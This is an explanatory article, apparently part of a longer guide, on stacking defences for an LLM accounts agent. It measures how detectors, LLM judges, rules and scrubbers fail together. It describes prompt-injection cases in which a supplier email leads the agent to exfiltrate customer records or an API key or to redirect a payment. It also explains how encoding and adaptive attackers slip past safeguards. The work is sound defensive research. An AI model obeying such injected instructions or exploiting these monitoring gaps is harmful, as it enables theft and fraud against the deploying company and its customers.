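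Asking the clerk for confirmation works only if it happens rarely. Narisetty and colleagues warn that people who see too many requests start approving them out of fatigue, and that an attacker can write the injection to persuade the person as well as the model. In tests by Li and colleagues, agents stopped for confirmation so often that the researchers had to instruct them not to, or the tests would have stalled. When the program does ask, it should show the recipient and the attachment directly from the tool call, because a summary by the agent could describe the email to outside.example as a routine backup.

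## Whether the layers fail independently

The usual argument for stacking layers assumes that they seldom miss the same attacks. *AI Alignment Strategies from a Risk Perspective* (Dung and Mai, 2025) shows why this matters with an example of ten safety techniques that each fail 10% of the time. If the failures are independent, all ten fail together once in ten billion cases. If all ten fail in exactly the same cases, the stack fails 10% of the time, as often as a single technique would.

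Real layers fall somewhere between failing independently and failing together. Developers seldom know how independent their own layers are because, as *DefenseComposer* (2026) points out, companies routinely stack defences while studies evaluate each one in isolation.

Software engineers faced this problem in the 1980s, when some hoped to make programs reliable by having several teams write the same program separately. *Builder, Defender, Breaker* (2026) recounts how Knight and Leveson tested the idea. The programs failed on the same inputs far more often than they would have if their failures were independent, because people with similar training make similar mistakes on the same difficult parts of a problem. AI-written code has the same weakness. In a recent study by Nogueira and colleagues, a majority vote among five programs from different models improved reliability by less than half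 as much as it would have if their errors were independent.

### How correlation changes the joint miss rate

Alotaibi and Ahmed (2026), in *How Diverse Are Layered Safeguards?*, give the exact formula for the share of attacks that two layers both miss:

joint miss = p₁p₂ + ρ √(p₁(1 − p₁) p₂(1 − p₂))

Here p₁ and p₂ are the two layers' miss rates, and p₁p₂ is the share of attacks both would miss if their errors were independent. The correlation ρ (rho) is zero if a miss by one layer doesn't change the chance of a miss by the other. It is positive if they tend to miss the same attacks, and negative if each tends to catch what the other misses. Multiplying ρ by the square root converts it into a share of attacks. The square root is small when either layer misses almost nothing or almost everything, because their errors then have little room to vary together.

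Suppose a detector and a validator each miss 10% of attacks. If their misses were independent, both would miss the same attack 1% of the time, so adding the second layer would cut misses by nine-tenths. If their misses have a correlation of 0.4, both miss 1% + 0.4 × (10% × 90%) = 4.6% of attacks, so the second layer cuts misses by only about half.

If the correlation between the layers stays the same, multiplying their miss rates underestimates joint misses by a larger factor as the layers improve. If each missed only 1%, multiplication would predict one joint miss in 10,000, but with the same correlation there would be about 41. *Physics in Safety and Safety in Physics* (2026), on the protection systems of the Large Hadron Collider, makes a similar point about physical barriers: when each barrier rarely fails on its own, even a small chance of a cause that defeats both can account for most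 of the remaining risk.

### Rules and judges on the same actions

The closest measurement for agents comes from *Evaluate the Stack, Not the Layer* (Yang, October 2026). Yang collected 1,119 proposed agent actions, 560 of them labeled as ones a layer should block, and ran five layers on all of them. One layer was a set of 174 text patterns that match dangerous actions. The other four were LLM judges (GPT-5.5 and three Claude models). Every layer read only the proposed action, without the user's request.

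| Pair | Missed by each alone | Missed by both, if independent | Missed by both, measured | Correlation | Equivalent layers |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Rules and a judge | 13.4% and 10.5% | 1.4% | 1.3% (7 of 560) | −0.02 | 2.1 |
| Two judges | 10.5% and 10.5% | 1.1% | 5.2% (29 of 560) | 0.43 | 1.3 |

The correlations come from putting the miss rates into the formula above. The rules and the judge missed about as many of the same actions as multiplying their miss rates would predict, while the two judges missed nearly five times as many as predicted.

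The last column is Yang's own measure, the number of multiplication-equivalent layers. It is the number of independent layers, each with the pair's typical miss rate, that would together miss as much as the real pair does:

n = ln(joint miss) / ln(g), where g = √(p₁p₂)

The value of n is 2 for two independent layers and 1 for two layers that have equal miss rates and always miss the same actions. If the miss rates differ, the minimum is slightly above 1 (1.06 for the rules and the judge), because the pair can't miss more actions than its better layer does. For the two judges, g is 0.105, so n = ln 0.052 / ln 0.105 = −2.96 / −2.25 ≈ 1.3. For the rules and the judge, g is √(0.134 × 0.105) = 0.119, so n = ln 0.0125 / ln 0.119 = −4.38 / −2.13 ≈ 2.1.

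Other pairings gave similar results. Any two of the four judges were worth 1.2 to 1.6 layers, and the rules combined with any one judge were worth 1.8 to 2.1. All four judges together were worth fewer than two. Using a second judge from another company didn't help much either. GPT-5.5 and a DeepSeek judge, which Yang tested separately on two of the three collections of actions, were worth about 1.3 layers.

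Kohli (2026), in *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes*, found the same weakness on a different task. Nine models from seven families judged how two sentences relate, such as whether one follows from the other, and Kohli compared their answers with the majority view of 100 people. All nine were wrong on 51 of 1,000 questions, whereas independent errors would have produced fewer than one such case. The average correlation between two models' errors was 0.39, which made the nine votes equivalent to about 2.2 independent ones. At that correlation, even an unlimited number of judges would be equivalent to only about 2.6. The questions had nothing to do with security, and people disagree on many of them, so the result supports the general pattern more than any particular number.

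The evidence that rules and judges fail independently is weaker than the evidence that judges fail together. There were only seven joint misses, and Yang's tests did not establish independence, so the failures may still be modestly correlated. Yang also built the rules and had tuned them on one of the three collections. On another team's set of risky shell commands, every layer missed most of the cases, and the misses by the rules and a judge fell only about midway between complete overlap and independence.

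The models behind the judges also changed. Yang asked for Claude Opus 5, but Opus 4.8 answered in 50 of 112 batches, and in 36 of those only the model name in the log showed the switch. In a repeat with fixed model versions, the older Sonnet 4.6 missed 21 of the 560 dangerous actions, while Sonnet 5 had missed 95 in the main test. The gap between the two kinds of pair stayed about the same, so it seems more reliable than any single miss rate.

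The most important limitation of Yang's study is that no attacker adapted to the layers. An attacker who knows the rules can word an action so that none of them matches, and then only has to fool the judge. A layer can also make far too many errors even if they are independent of the other layers' errors. Without any attacker, the rules missed 52.9% of dangerous actions in a collection about cloud systems, which they weren't written to cover.

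### Why accuracy doesn't show what a layer adds

A company adding another layer would probably compare the miss rates of the options and choose the one with the lowest. Yang tested that approach by adding different layers to stacks of three judges and counting the dangerous actions that only the new layer caught. The counts below are totals over the four possible stacks.

| Layer added | Missed alone | Extra actions caught |
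|---|---|---|
| Rules | 13.9% | 86 |
| Rules plus a pack of cloud rules | 11.1% | 86 |
| A fourth judge | 13.3% | 22 |
| A simple list of 50 patterns | 85.7% | 9 |

The rules and the fourth judge were about equally accurate, but the rules added almost four times as much to the stack. The cloud pack cut the rules' miss rate on their own by a fifth but did not improve the stack, because the judges already caught the extra actions it detected. The list of 50 patterns missed six in seven dangerous actions but caught a few that three judges had missed.

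Each layer could return "review", which passes the action to a person. The table counts a review as a miss, which affects GPT-5.5 most because it returned "review" on 47 of the 560 dangerous actions, while the other judges did so between 2 and 17 times. GPT-5.5's miss rate is 9.8% in the table, which is ordinary among the judges, but it would be 1.4%, easily the best, if reviews counted as catches.

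Five of Yang's conclusions reversed depending on whether reviews counted as catches, and counting them favoured the judge that escalated most each time. The headline pairs in the earlier table count reviews as catches, but the difference between rules and judges holds either way. For the accounts agent, a review is a catch only if the clerk reads it and stops the bad payment.

### Hard cases

Two judges can miss the same dangerous actions because those actions are hard to recognise, even if the judges share no particular flaw. Suppose 21% of dangerous actions are hard to recognise and the rest are easy. Each judge catches every easy one and misses half of the hard ones, independently of the other judge. Each judge then misses 10.5% of the total, and both miss a quarter of the hard ones, or about 5.2% of the total. Yang measured these same rates, so differences in difficulty alone could explain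 them.

If two judges share a flaw from similar training, a different kind of judge could fix it. If some actions are hard to judge from their text, another judge that reads the same text will struggle too, and it may be better to give the judges more information, such as the user's request or a label showing where an account number came from. Yang couldn't settle which explanation fits. The difficulty of the actions accounted for 32% to 62% of the judges' excess joint misses, depending on the method.

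Alotaibi and Ahmed studied the same question with an adaptive attacker. They placed seven safeguards around Vicuna-7B, a small open model from 2023, and an automated attacker tried to get answers to 100 harmful requests. It faced each safeguard separately and ran three times. The correlations between pairs of safeguards ranged from 0.49 to 0.65, excluding the strongest safeguard, a classifier that blocked nearly everything.

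The safeguards failed together partly because some requests were easy to get answered whichever safeguard was used. Even with no safeguards, two runs of the same attack succeeded on much the same requests, with a correlation of 0.62. Adjusting for how easily each request succeeded against the unprotected model cut the average correlation between the safeguards' failures from 0.585 to 0.171, a drop of 71%. On Llama-2-7B, which refuses more readily, the difficulty of the requests explained only 34% of the correlation.

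The attacker also faced the safeguards together. Six of them, without the strong classifier, let through 57.3% of attacks. The expected rate was 47.3%, the share of attacks that had beaten all six when the attacker faced them one at a time. The six together still did better than the best single safeguard, which let through 64.7%, but the improvement was less than half of what was expected.

Layers that flag the same harmless messages should spoil fewer tasks than layers that err independently, but combining the safeguards removed this advantage. When seven safeguards each ran alone, at least one of them refused 60 of 100 harmless requests, compared with the 81 expected if their errors had been independent. The combined stack refused 83, including 23 that no safeguard had refused alone, partly because some safeguards change the text that the model or the next safeguard reads.

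These measurements tested safeguards against harmful requests on old, small models, with no tools and no planted instructions, so the percentages probably don't carry over to the accounts agent. But they are a reason to distrust any error rate for a whole stack that was calculated from the error rates of its layers. The strong classifier let through 3% of the first attacker's attempts and 19% of a second attacker's, although the second tried about a thirtieth as many prompts. A miss rate, and any correlation based on it, therefore applies only to the attacker it was measured against.

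### Which miss rates can be multiplied

Yang's five layers all checked the same action for the same thing, whereas the four layers around the accounts agent check different things for different problems. A redactor doesn't catch the injections that a detector misses, so multiplying their miss rates is meaningless.

*Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (Darapaneni, Padmaja K and Gnana Chaithra D, 2026) observes that adding layers multiplies protection only where each layer can inspect the attack. In its model, which uses invented rates, 6% of injections typed by the user get past three layers, but 42% of injections in retrieved documents do, because the filter on the user's message never reads those documents. Some attacks pass all three layers and meet only one control that can stop them.

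Suppose each of the four layers misses 10% of what it is meant to catch, and all their errors are independent. The stack would then miss one in 10,000 of the attacks that all four layers are meant to catch, but a larger share of those that fewer layers cover. The table shows what the stack would do with four failures of the accounts agent under these assumptions.

| Failure | Layers that could stop it | Missed by all of them |
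|---|---|---|
| The model's provider receives the customer's bank details | Redaction | 10% |
| The agent refunds the wrong customer by mistake | Output validation | 10% |
| A supplier's email redirects a payment | Injection detector, output validation | 1% |
| A supplier's email gets the agent to send out the API key | Credential scrubbing, injection detector, output validation | 0.1% |

Nothing in the table reaches one in 10,000, and an extra layer that improves the last row may do nothing for the first two.

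### The theft of an API key

The last row is a chain of three events. The model reads the key because the scrubber missed it, the detector misses the injection, and the output validator passes the call that sends the key out. The probability of theft is a product in which each link depends on the ones before it:

P(theft) = P(key visible) × P(injection missed, given key visible) × P(call passed, given both)

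This product is always correct. Its last term should be the validator's miss rate on calls from attacks the detector has already missed, because only those calls matter here. Using the validator's miss rate from a general test is a mistake.

This example uses illustrative numbers and assumes that the model obeys any injection it reads. The key is visible in 5% of attacks. In those cases, the detector misses 20% of injections, and the validator would pass 10% of the malicious calls if every attack reached it. If the errors are independent, attackers steal the key in 0.05 × 0.2 × 0.1 of attacks, or 1 in 1,000.

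The detector and the validator let more attacks through if they tend to miss the same ones. With individual miss rates of 20% and 10%, both would miss 2% of attacks if their misses were independent. With a correlation of 0.4, close to what Yang's two judges showed, both would miss 0.2 × 0.1 + 0.4 × √(0.2 × 0.8 × 0.1 × 0.9) = 6.8%.

| Correlation between the last two errors | Calls passed after a missed injection | Thefts per 10,000 attacks |
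|---|---|---|
| 0 | 10% | 10 |
| 0.2 | 22% | 22 |
| 0.4 | 34% | 34 |
| 0.67, the highest possible | 50% | 50 |

A correlation of 0.4 between the detector's misses and the validator's more than triples the thefts, even though each layer's own miss rate stays the same. The detector misses 20% of attacks and the validator misses 10%, so the correlation can't exceed 0.67, which it reaches when the detector misses every attack that the validator misses.

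The last two errors are likely to be correlated if both layers are language models. If an email's wording leads the detector to classify a request as routine, it may lead an LLM judge to do the same. Darapaneni and colleagues warn that layers fail together if they are built on the same model family or can't read the same language. A rule that checks the recipient doesn't depend on the wording, so its errors should be less correlated with the detector's. Yang's result for rules and judges is consistent with this, but those layers read the same text, whereas here the detector reads an email and the rule reads a tool call.

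Even a rule can fail for the same reason as the detector. If an attacker takes over the mailbox of an approved supplier, the email can quote real orders in the supplier's usual style, and the key goes to an address on the approved list. Suppose 2% of attacks come from such a mailbox and always pass both checks, and errors are otherwise independent. Thefts would roughly double, from 10 to 20 per 10,000.

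A credential vault acts on the first link, whether the key is visible. If it cuts the share of attacks in which the key is visible from 5% to 0.5%, thefts fall by 90% at every correlation in the table. *Caging the Agents* (2026), a security design for healthcare agents, relies on this. Its instructions to the model about untrusted text are the weakest of its four layers, but its vault and its limits on where the agent can send data still work if the model follows an injected instruction.

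An attacker can redirect a payment without seeing a key, so of the three layers only the detector and the validator can stop the attack. With the same inputs, 200 attacks in 10,000 would succeed if the two layers' errors were independent, and 680 would succeed if the correlation were 0.4. The correlation therefore matters most for harmful actions, where secret scrubbing doesn't limit the damage.

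Repeated attempts change the calculation again. A supplier can send a hundred emails, but if the scrubber misses a key in a configuration file once, it will probably miss it every time. If the 5% is the chance that the company has such a key, and the emails are otherwise independent attempts, the chance that at least one email steals it is 0.05 × (1 − 0.98¹⁰⁰), or 4.3%. At a correlation of 0.4, it is almost exactly 5%. After enough attempts, the two later layers hardly matter, and the outcome depends on whether the company has such a key. However, the detector would flag about 80 of the hundred emails, so somebody who investigated the flags could block the sender early on.

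Estimating each phase of an attack separately is risky even when the attacker doesn't adapt. *Harmonizing AI Safety Thresholds* (2026) gives two estimates of how often an AI-assisted cyberattack would succeed from start to finish. Multiplying the chances of success for each phase gives 8.4%, while estimating the attack as a whole gives 60%. The sevenfold gap is still unexplained.

A company can measure the whole chain by putting a fake key in a test copy of the accounts agent, sending it planted emails and counting how often the key gets out. The test is more useful if it also records where each failed attack stopped. In *Measuring LLM Agent Defenses by Layer*, Han (2026) recorded this for 1,000 attacks on 15 combinations of agent program and model by capturing everything that passed between the two. Han sorted the results by whether the model refused, stopped partway, carried out the attack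 but was blocked by the agent program, or succeeded. A single success rate would not distinguish a model that recognises attacks from one that obeys them behind a good filter. For the accounts agent, the same kind of record would show how many malicious calls the validator passes among the attacks that the detector has missed, which is the number needed to measure the last link.

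## How order and interaction change the result

A later layer in the accounts agent reads only what the earlier layers pass on. An earlier layer can remove text that a later one needs, add text that causes it to make errors, or control which emails reach it. Two layers that each work well alone can therefore work badly together, and swapping their order can change the result.

### Three choices of order

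These three cases are reasoning about the accounts agent, not measurements.

The planted instruction in the supplier's email is to send customer records to archive@outside.example. If redaction runs before injection detection, the detector receives only [EMAIL_1] in place of the address, which could just as well be a colleague's. If detection runs first, the detector receives the full address, along with any personal data in the email. That does little harm if the detector is a small classifier on the company's own machines. But if it is an LLM judge at an outside provider, the company has disclosed the data that redaction was meant to protect. A local detector should therefore probably run before redaction and a hosted one after it. A placeholder such as [EXTERNAL_EMAIL_1] would preserve the most useful fact for the hosted detector, which is that the address is outside the company.

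A similar choice arises when some configuration files store keys in Base64, which writes any data using 64 ordinary characters. An AWS key that starts with AKIA starts with QUtJQ in Base64, so a scrubber that looks for the usual prefix misses the key, even though anyone who receives the file can decode it. Decoding first reveals the prefix, but an agent that has to edit the file needs the original encoding. The scrubber could decode a copy, scan both versions, and remove any key it finds from the original.

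The last case is the outgoing scan. If it runs before the program restores placeholders, an email to a stranger passes because it contains only [ACCOUNT_1], and the program then inserts the real number. If the scan runs after restoration, it finds that number, but it also finds an account number in every correct refund. Scanning both before and after restoration seems best. A real account number in the model's output before restoration suggests that the redactor missed it, because the model should have had only the placeholder. After restoration, the program has both the real number and the destination, so a rule can let the number go only to the payment system.

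### A title that lost a word

*DefenseComposer* (Chen, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested a different pair of layers, Spotlighting and CommandSans, in both orders. Spotlighting adds an eight-character marker to untrusted text so that the model treats the text as data. CommandSans deletes text that looks like a command but skips anything shorter than eight characters.

An agent had to copy the title "Help me" from one file to another. CommandSans would normally have skipped the title because it has only seven characters, but Spotlighting ran first and its markers made the text longer. CommandSans then deleted "Help" as a command, and the agent wrote only "me". When CommandSans ran first, the agent copied the title correctly in all four runs.

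Changing the order doesn't fix every conflict. Spotlighting also added its marker to a file's ID number, so the file tool couldn't find the file. The researchers had to exempt ID numbers from marking. An accounts agent could have the same problem with order numbers. In another case, two cleaning layers removed details the task needed, regardless of which layer ran first.

### Thirteen defences in 66 arrangements

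Chen and colleagues tested 13 defences that act on the text the model reads, on its tools, or on what the tools return. They ran 66 arrangements of up to four defences with Gemini 2.5 Flash on AgentDojo. Each arrangement had 40 runs without an attack and 240 with one.

| Defences | Harmless tasks completed | Attacks that succeeded | Tokens relative to no defence |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 80.0% | 13.3% | 1.00 |
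| Delimiters around tool output | 92.5% | 11.2% | 1.29 |
| Filter that limits the available tools | 52.5% | 4.2% | 0.47 |
| Delimiters and tool filter | 77.5% | 0.4% | 0.60 |
| Spotlighting | 67.5% | 2.5% | 1.12 |
| CommandSans | 72.5% | 8.8% | 2.85 |
| Spotlighting and CommandSans | 20.0% | 3.3% | 2.70 |
| Both of these, a second cleaner and an action check | 5.0% | 0.0% | 3.14 |

Delimiters and the tool filter together let through far fewer attacks than either alone, and the agent completed more tasks than with the filter alone. Spotlighting and CommandSans combined poorly. Spotlighting alone reduced task completion by 12.5 points, and CommandSans alone reduced it by 7.5. If those reductions had simply added up, the agent would have completed 60% of tasks with both defenses, but it completed only 20%.

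No attack succeeded against the stack of four defences, mainly because the agent completed almost no tasks. The researchers attributed 30 of its 38 failures on harmless tasks to interactions between defences and only six to a single defence. The model's tool call was often malformed. The drop in completion also depends on the model, since agents with the same stack completed 47.5% of tasks with Qwen-Max and 50.0% with DeepSeek-V4-Pro. With Gemini, recording where each cleaned passage came from raised completion from 5.0% to 35.0%, and still no attacks succeeded.

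A second defence usually added little protection. Pairs of defences that worked only on text reduced attack success by an average of 0.3 points compared with the defence in the pair that let through fewer attacks alone. They also completed 19.8 points fewer tasks than the defence that completed more alone. When a text defence was paired with a tool filter or an action check, attack success fell by 0.5 points and task completion by 16.0. This comparison puts pairs at a disadvantage because it measures them against the better single defence for each result, which may not be the same defence both times.

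The stack of four also did no better against attacks written for the complete arrangement. Eight out of 100 succeeded, the same number as against delimiters and the tool filter.

These 66 arrangements never include the same two defences in both orders, so the evidence about order comes from a few traced tasks. The evidence about combinations is much stronger, and it also helped with repairs. A coding agent using GPT-6 Astra repaired six other pairs with the help of rules drawn from the failures, and completion of harmless tasks rose from 66.7% to 100%. When the agent had only the source code, completion reached 85.4%, and its changes made two of the six pairs worse.

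### False data that an earlier layer lets through

A later layer can also make the wrong decision because it relies on false data. *PIPES* (Kariyappa, Klingler and Suh, 2026) gives the example of an agent that has to order from the highest-rated restaurant. A restaurant owner puts a false rating in a field meant for menu tags. The agent uses this rating and orders from that restaurant, and an LLM judge approves the order because it seems to match the user's request.

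The researchers tested this kind of attack on agents that order deliveries, book local services and arrange travel. The attacker could revise the text up to ten times and read the defence's reasoning. With Gemma 4 31B, an open Google model, an average of 89% of attacks succeeded without a defence and 39% with a judge checking each action. PIPES, which checks whether each part of a tool's response comes from a source entitled to provide that information, reduced the success rate to 2.8%. The action check also reduced completion of AgentDyn's shopping and software tasks from 95% to 70%.

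PIPES had the advantage of prepared descriptions of what each field should contain. Still, the result points to a risk for the accounts agent. A rule that caps refunds at the order price protects the company only if the price comes from the company's own records. If the price comes from the supplier's email, the supplier can raise the cap.

### Why removing a layer differs from replacing it

Developers often measure a layer's contribution by switching it off and counting the extra attacks that get through. Abasıkeleş-Turgut and Gümüş (2026) show in *Deletion Is Not Substitution* that this can be misleading, using BARBICAN, a gateway for agents' tool calls that their research group built.

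BARBICAN's documentation describes four tiers: text rules, a comparison with known kinds of attack, a calibrator that adapts thresholds to recent traffic, and a classifier for uncertain cases. The researchers recorded how every stage handled 25,000 prompts and found ten differences from that description. The calibrator used fixed thresholds. A memory of 118 stored patterns, which isn't one of the four tiers, blocked 2,132 prompts outright. The classifier's main route for clearing harmless prompts never cleared one.

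They then changed the classifier in several ways:

| Change | Decisions that changed |
|---|---|
| Switch it off and treat its prompts as allowed | 674 |
| Switch it off and leave its prompts unresolved | 135 |
| Switch it off and treat its prompts as attacks | 12 |
| Make it always answer "attack" | 12 |
| Make it always answer "harmless" | 140 |
| Replace it with Prompt Guard 2 | 16 |
| Put Prompt Guard 2 in the earlier comparison tier instead | 1,015 |

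The first three rows all describe removing the classifier and differ only in what happens to the prompts it would have judged. Switching the classifier off therefore measures the effect of the rule for handling those prompts as well as the effect of losing the classifier. Holding its answer constant leaves that rule in place, so any change in the result comes from the answer alone.

About 97% of the 7,453 prompts that reached the classifier were attacks, and BARBICAN blocked nearly all of them regardless of the classifier's verdict. A harmless verdict could release only 152 prompts, all of them attacks, so even a perfect classifier could do no better than one that always answered "attack". Prompt Guard 2 correctly recognised 202 harmless prompts, but BARBICAN blocked those too.

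The accounts agent could have the same fault. Suppose a detector sends suspicious emails to an LLM judge, and the program delivers a flagged email only if the judge clears it and it comes from an approved supplier. A better judge wouldn't help a new supplier whose harmless email the detector had flagged.

This evidence comes from one gateway, and the test classified prompts without running an agent. BARBICAN caught 80.7% of attacks on its own benchmark but only 31.2% on an independent set. In a simulation with public classifiers, removal and replacement gave results of similar size when about half the uncertain prompts were attacks. The problem seems to arise mainly when earlier layers pass on almost nothing but attacks, or when later rules ignore the verdict. The researchers reviewed 19 layered defences and found reported tests that removed or isolated components for 16 of them, but a full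 explanation of what happened to the affected inputs for only one.

### Which layer gets the credit

Removing a layer also shows its effect only on the attacks tested. *ChannelGuard* (Hossain, Nipu and colleagues, 2026) places gates on the text passing between several cooperating models. Each gate compares the text with 20 known attack phrases. Removing the gate on the user's message raised the attack success rate from 3% to 73% on Qwen3-4B and from 10% to 77% on Llama-3.1-8B. Removing any of the other gates tested had no effect on either model.

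Every attack in the removal test was in the user's message, so the test doesn't show that the other gates can be deleted. In separate tests, the gate on tool output blocked all 30 attacks hidden there on each of five models. None of the gates worked well against attacks with new wording, which succeeded 60% of the time on Qwen with ChannelGuard and 63% without it.

Hossain and colleagues also recorded what stopped each attack. Without ChannelGuard, Llama safely handled all 90 attacks in tool output and memory on its own. With ChannelGuard, the gates were credited with blocking all 90, even though none would have succeeded without them. The gates could still be useful if the company changed models, since six of the same 90 attacks succeeded on undefended Qwen. On GPT-5, Microsoft's cloud filter stopped 54 of the 90, and the company could lose that protection by changing providers.

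Han makes a similar attribution using recordings of the traffic between the agent program and the model. Neither the agent nor the attacker can alter these recordings. If the program blocks an action and the model then recognises the attack and refuses to continue, Han credits the program.

These shares also depend on each layer's position. Suppose the model in the accounts agent refuses 750 of 1,000 attacks, and the program blocks 200 of the remaining 250. The program has stopped 20% of all attacks but 80% of those that reached it. If the company switches to a model that refuses 900, and the program still blocks 80% of what reaches it, the program would stop only 80 attacks, or 8% of the total. A team should therefore report each layer's result as a share of the attacks that reached it, though those attacks may become harder to block when the model improves.

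### Adding up the costs

Most of a stack's delay usually comes from extra model calls. Pattern matching and small classifiers are fast by comparison. Each ChannelGuard gate takes about five milliseconds, and the fastest redactor described earlier took about 13 milliseconds per résumé.

Koutidis, Kekatos and colleagues (2026), in *Constrained-Action AI Remediation for SIEM/XDR via a NeMo-Guardrails Proxy*, measured a slower arrangement on one Apple computer. They put NVIDIA's NeMo Guardrails around a 14-billion-parameter model that reads security alerts. One model call checks the input, another writes the reply and a third checks the output. They tested this setup on 200 attacks and 1,000 harmless log lines, and also tried adding checks that need less computation before the guardrails.

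| Arrangement | Attacks caught | Model calls per request | Median delay |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model alone | 25.0% | 1 | 0.31 s |
| NeMo Guardrails | 94.5% | 3.00 | 14.14 s |
| Decoding and pattern check, then NeMo | 95.0% | 2.88 | 14.11 s |
| Small model, then NeMo only for suspicious requests | 58.0% | 1.15 | 0.18 s |

NeMo flagged only one harmless line, so in this test delay was almost the only drawback of better detection for the company. At 14 seconds a call, a refund with 20 model calls would take nearly five minutes. But the gap exaggerates the delay that the checks would add to ordinary work, because the 0.31 seconds covered only a classification, not a full reply. NeMo blocked attacks in about half a second, which suggests that the input check was quick and that writing the reply and checking the output took most of the time.

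The last row shows the danger of putting a small detector first. Any attack that the small model cleared skipped NeMo, so the stack missed it too. When NeMo instead checked everything the small model had cleared, detection returned to 95.0%, but the average rose to 3.64 calls. The 1.15 figure also seems to leave out the main model's call for cleared requests, which would bring the average to about two. The decoding step was a safer addition, although the researchers had designed it to undo the same disguises they used in the test.

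*The Price of Safety* (Bhowmik, 2026) measured how many extra tokens four defences for an agent's memory used in ordinary conversations with no attacks. A pattern filter and a check on the source of each message used none. An LLM check on new messages added 1.5%, and an LLM check on retrieved memories added 3.0%. All four together added 4.5%, the sum of their separate increases.

The stack had no detectable effect on accuracy, but the test could have missed a loss of a few points. When used alone, the check on retrieved memories withheld at least one memory on 14.9% of questions. In a sample of 50 withheld memories, a reviewer found good reason to distrust only two. Most of the omissions didn't change the answer, but withholding a customer's new address from an accounts agent could matter more.

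When defenses are combined, their total delay is harder to predict than their total token use. In the tests by Chen and colleagues, an action check alone took about 57 seconds per harmless task and CommandSans alone took about 116, but together they took 935. The combination used only slightly more tokens than CommandSans alone, so much of the extra time probably came from something other than computing, such as retries or a provider's limit on requests. Bhowmik reports tokens instead of delay partly because such limits distort timings.

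The combined false-alarm rate is simple to calculate only if the layers don't affect each other. If redaction, detection and validation each independently spoiled 2% of refunds, together they would spoil about 5.9%. Spotlighting and CommandSans show how far the real figure can exceed this estimate.

### How to test a stack

For the accounts agent, these results suggest the following procedure:

1. Record what each layer receives and passes on, and compare this with the documentation. When Bhowmik first combined the four memory defences, one lost access to the memory and failed on every question. It crashed, but a silent failure could have looked like a valid result.
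2. Repeat the same harmless refunds several times with the same model version. Two of Bhowmik's defences never blocked anything, yet accuracy in one conversation still differed by up to nine points from the undefended run. In an earlier version of the study, a change of model accounted for 2.9 of the 4.4 points of accuracy loss that Bhowmik had blamed on a defence.
3. Run all 16 combinations of the four layers, including none and all, on the same tasks and attacks. If that takes too long, run the agent with no layers, each layer alone, the full stack, and the full stack without each layer in turn, which makes ten. Report completed refunds alongside successful attacks.
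4. Try both orders wherever one layer changes text that another reads, and check that order numbers, file names and addresses arrive unchanged.
5. If a layer receives only some of the traffic, make it always answer "harmless" and then always "attack". If neither changes any decisions, a better model in that position won't help.
6. Plant attacks in every channel and record which layer stops each one. Then switch that layer off and repeat the attack to find out whether another would have stopped it.
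7. Let an attacker adapt to the finished stack, since attacks written for one layer may never reach the others.

The number of attacks matters too. If none of 40 attacks succeeds, the true success rate could still be almost 9%. Lowering that upper limit to 1% would take about 380 attacks without a success.
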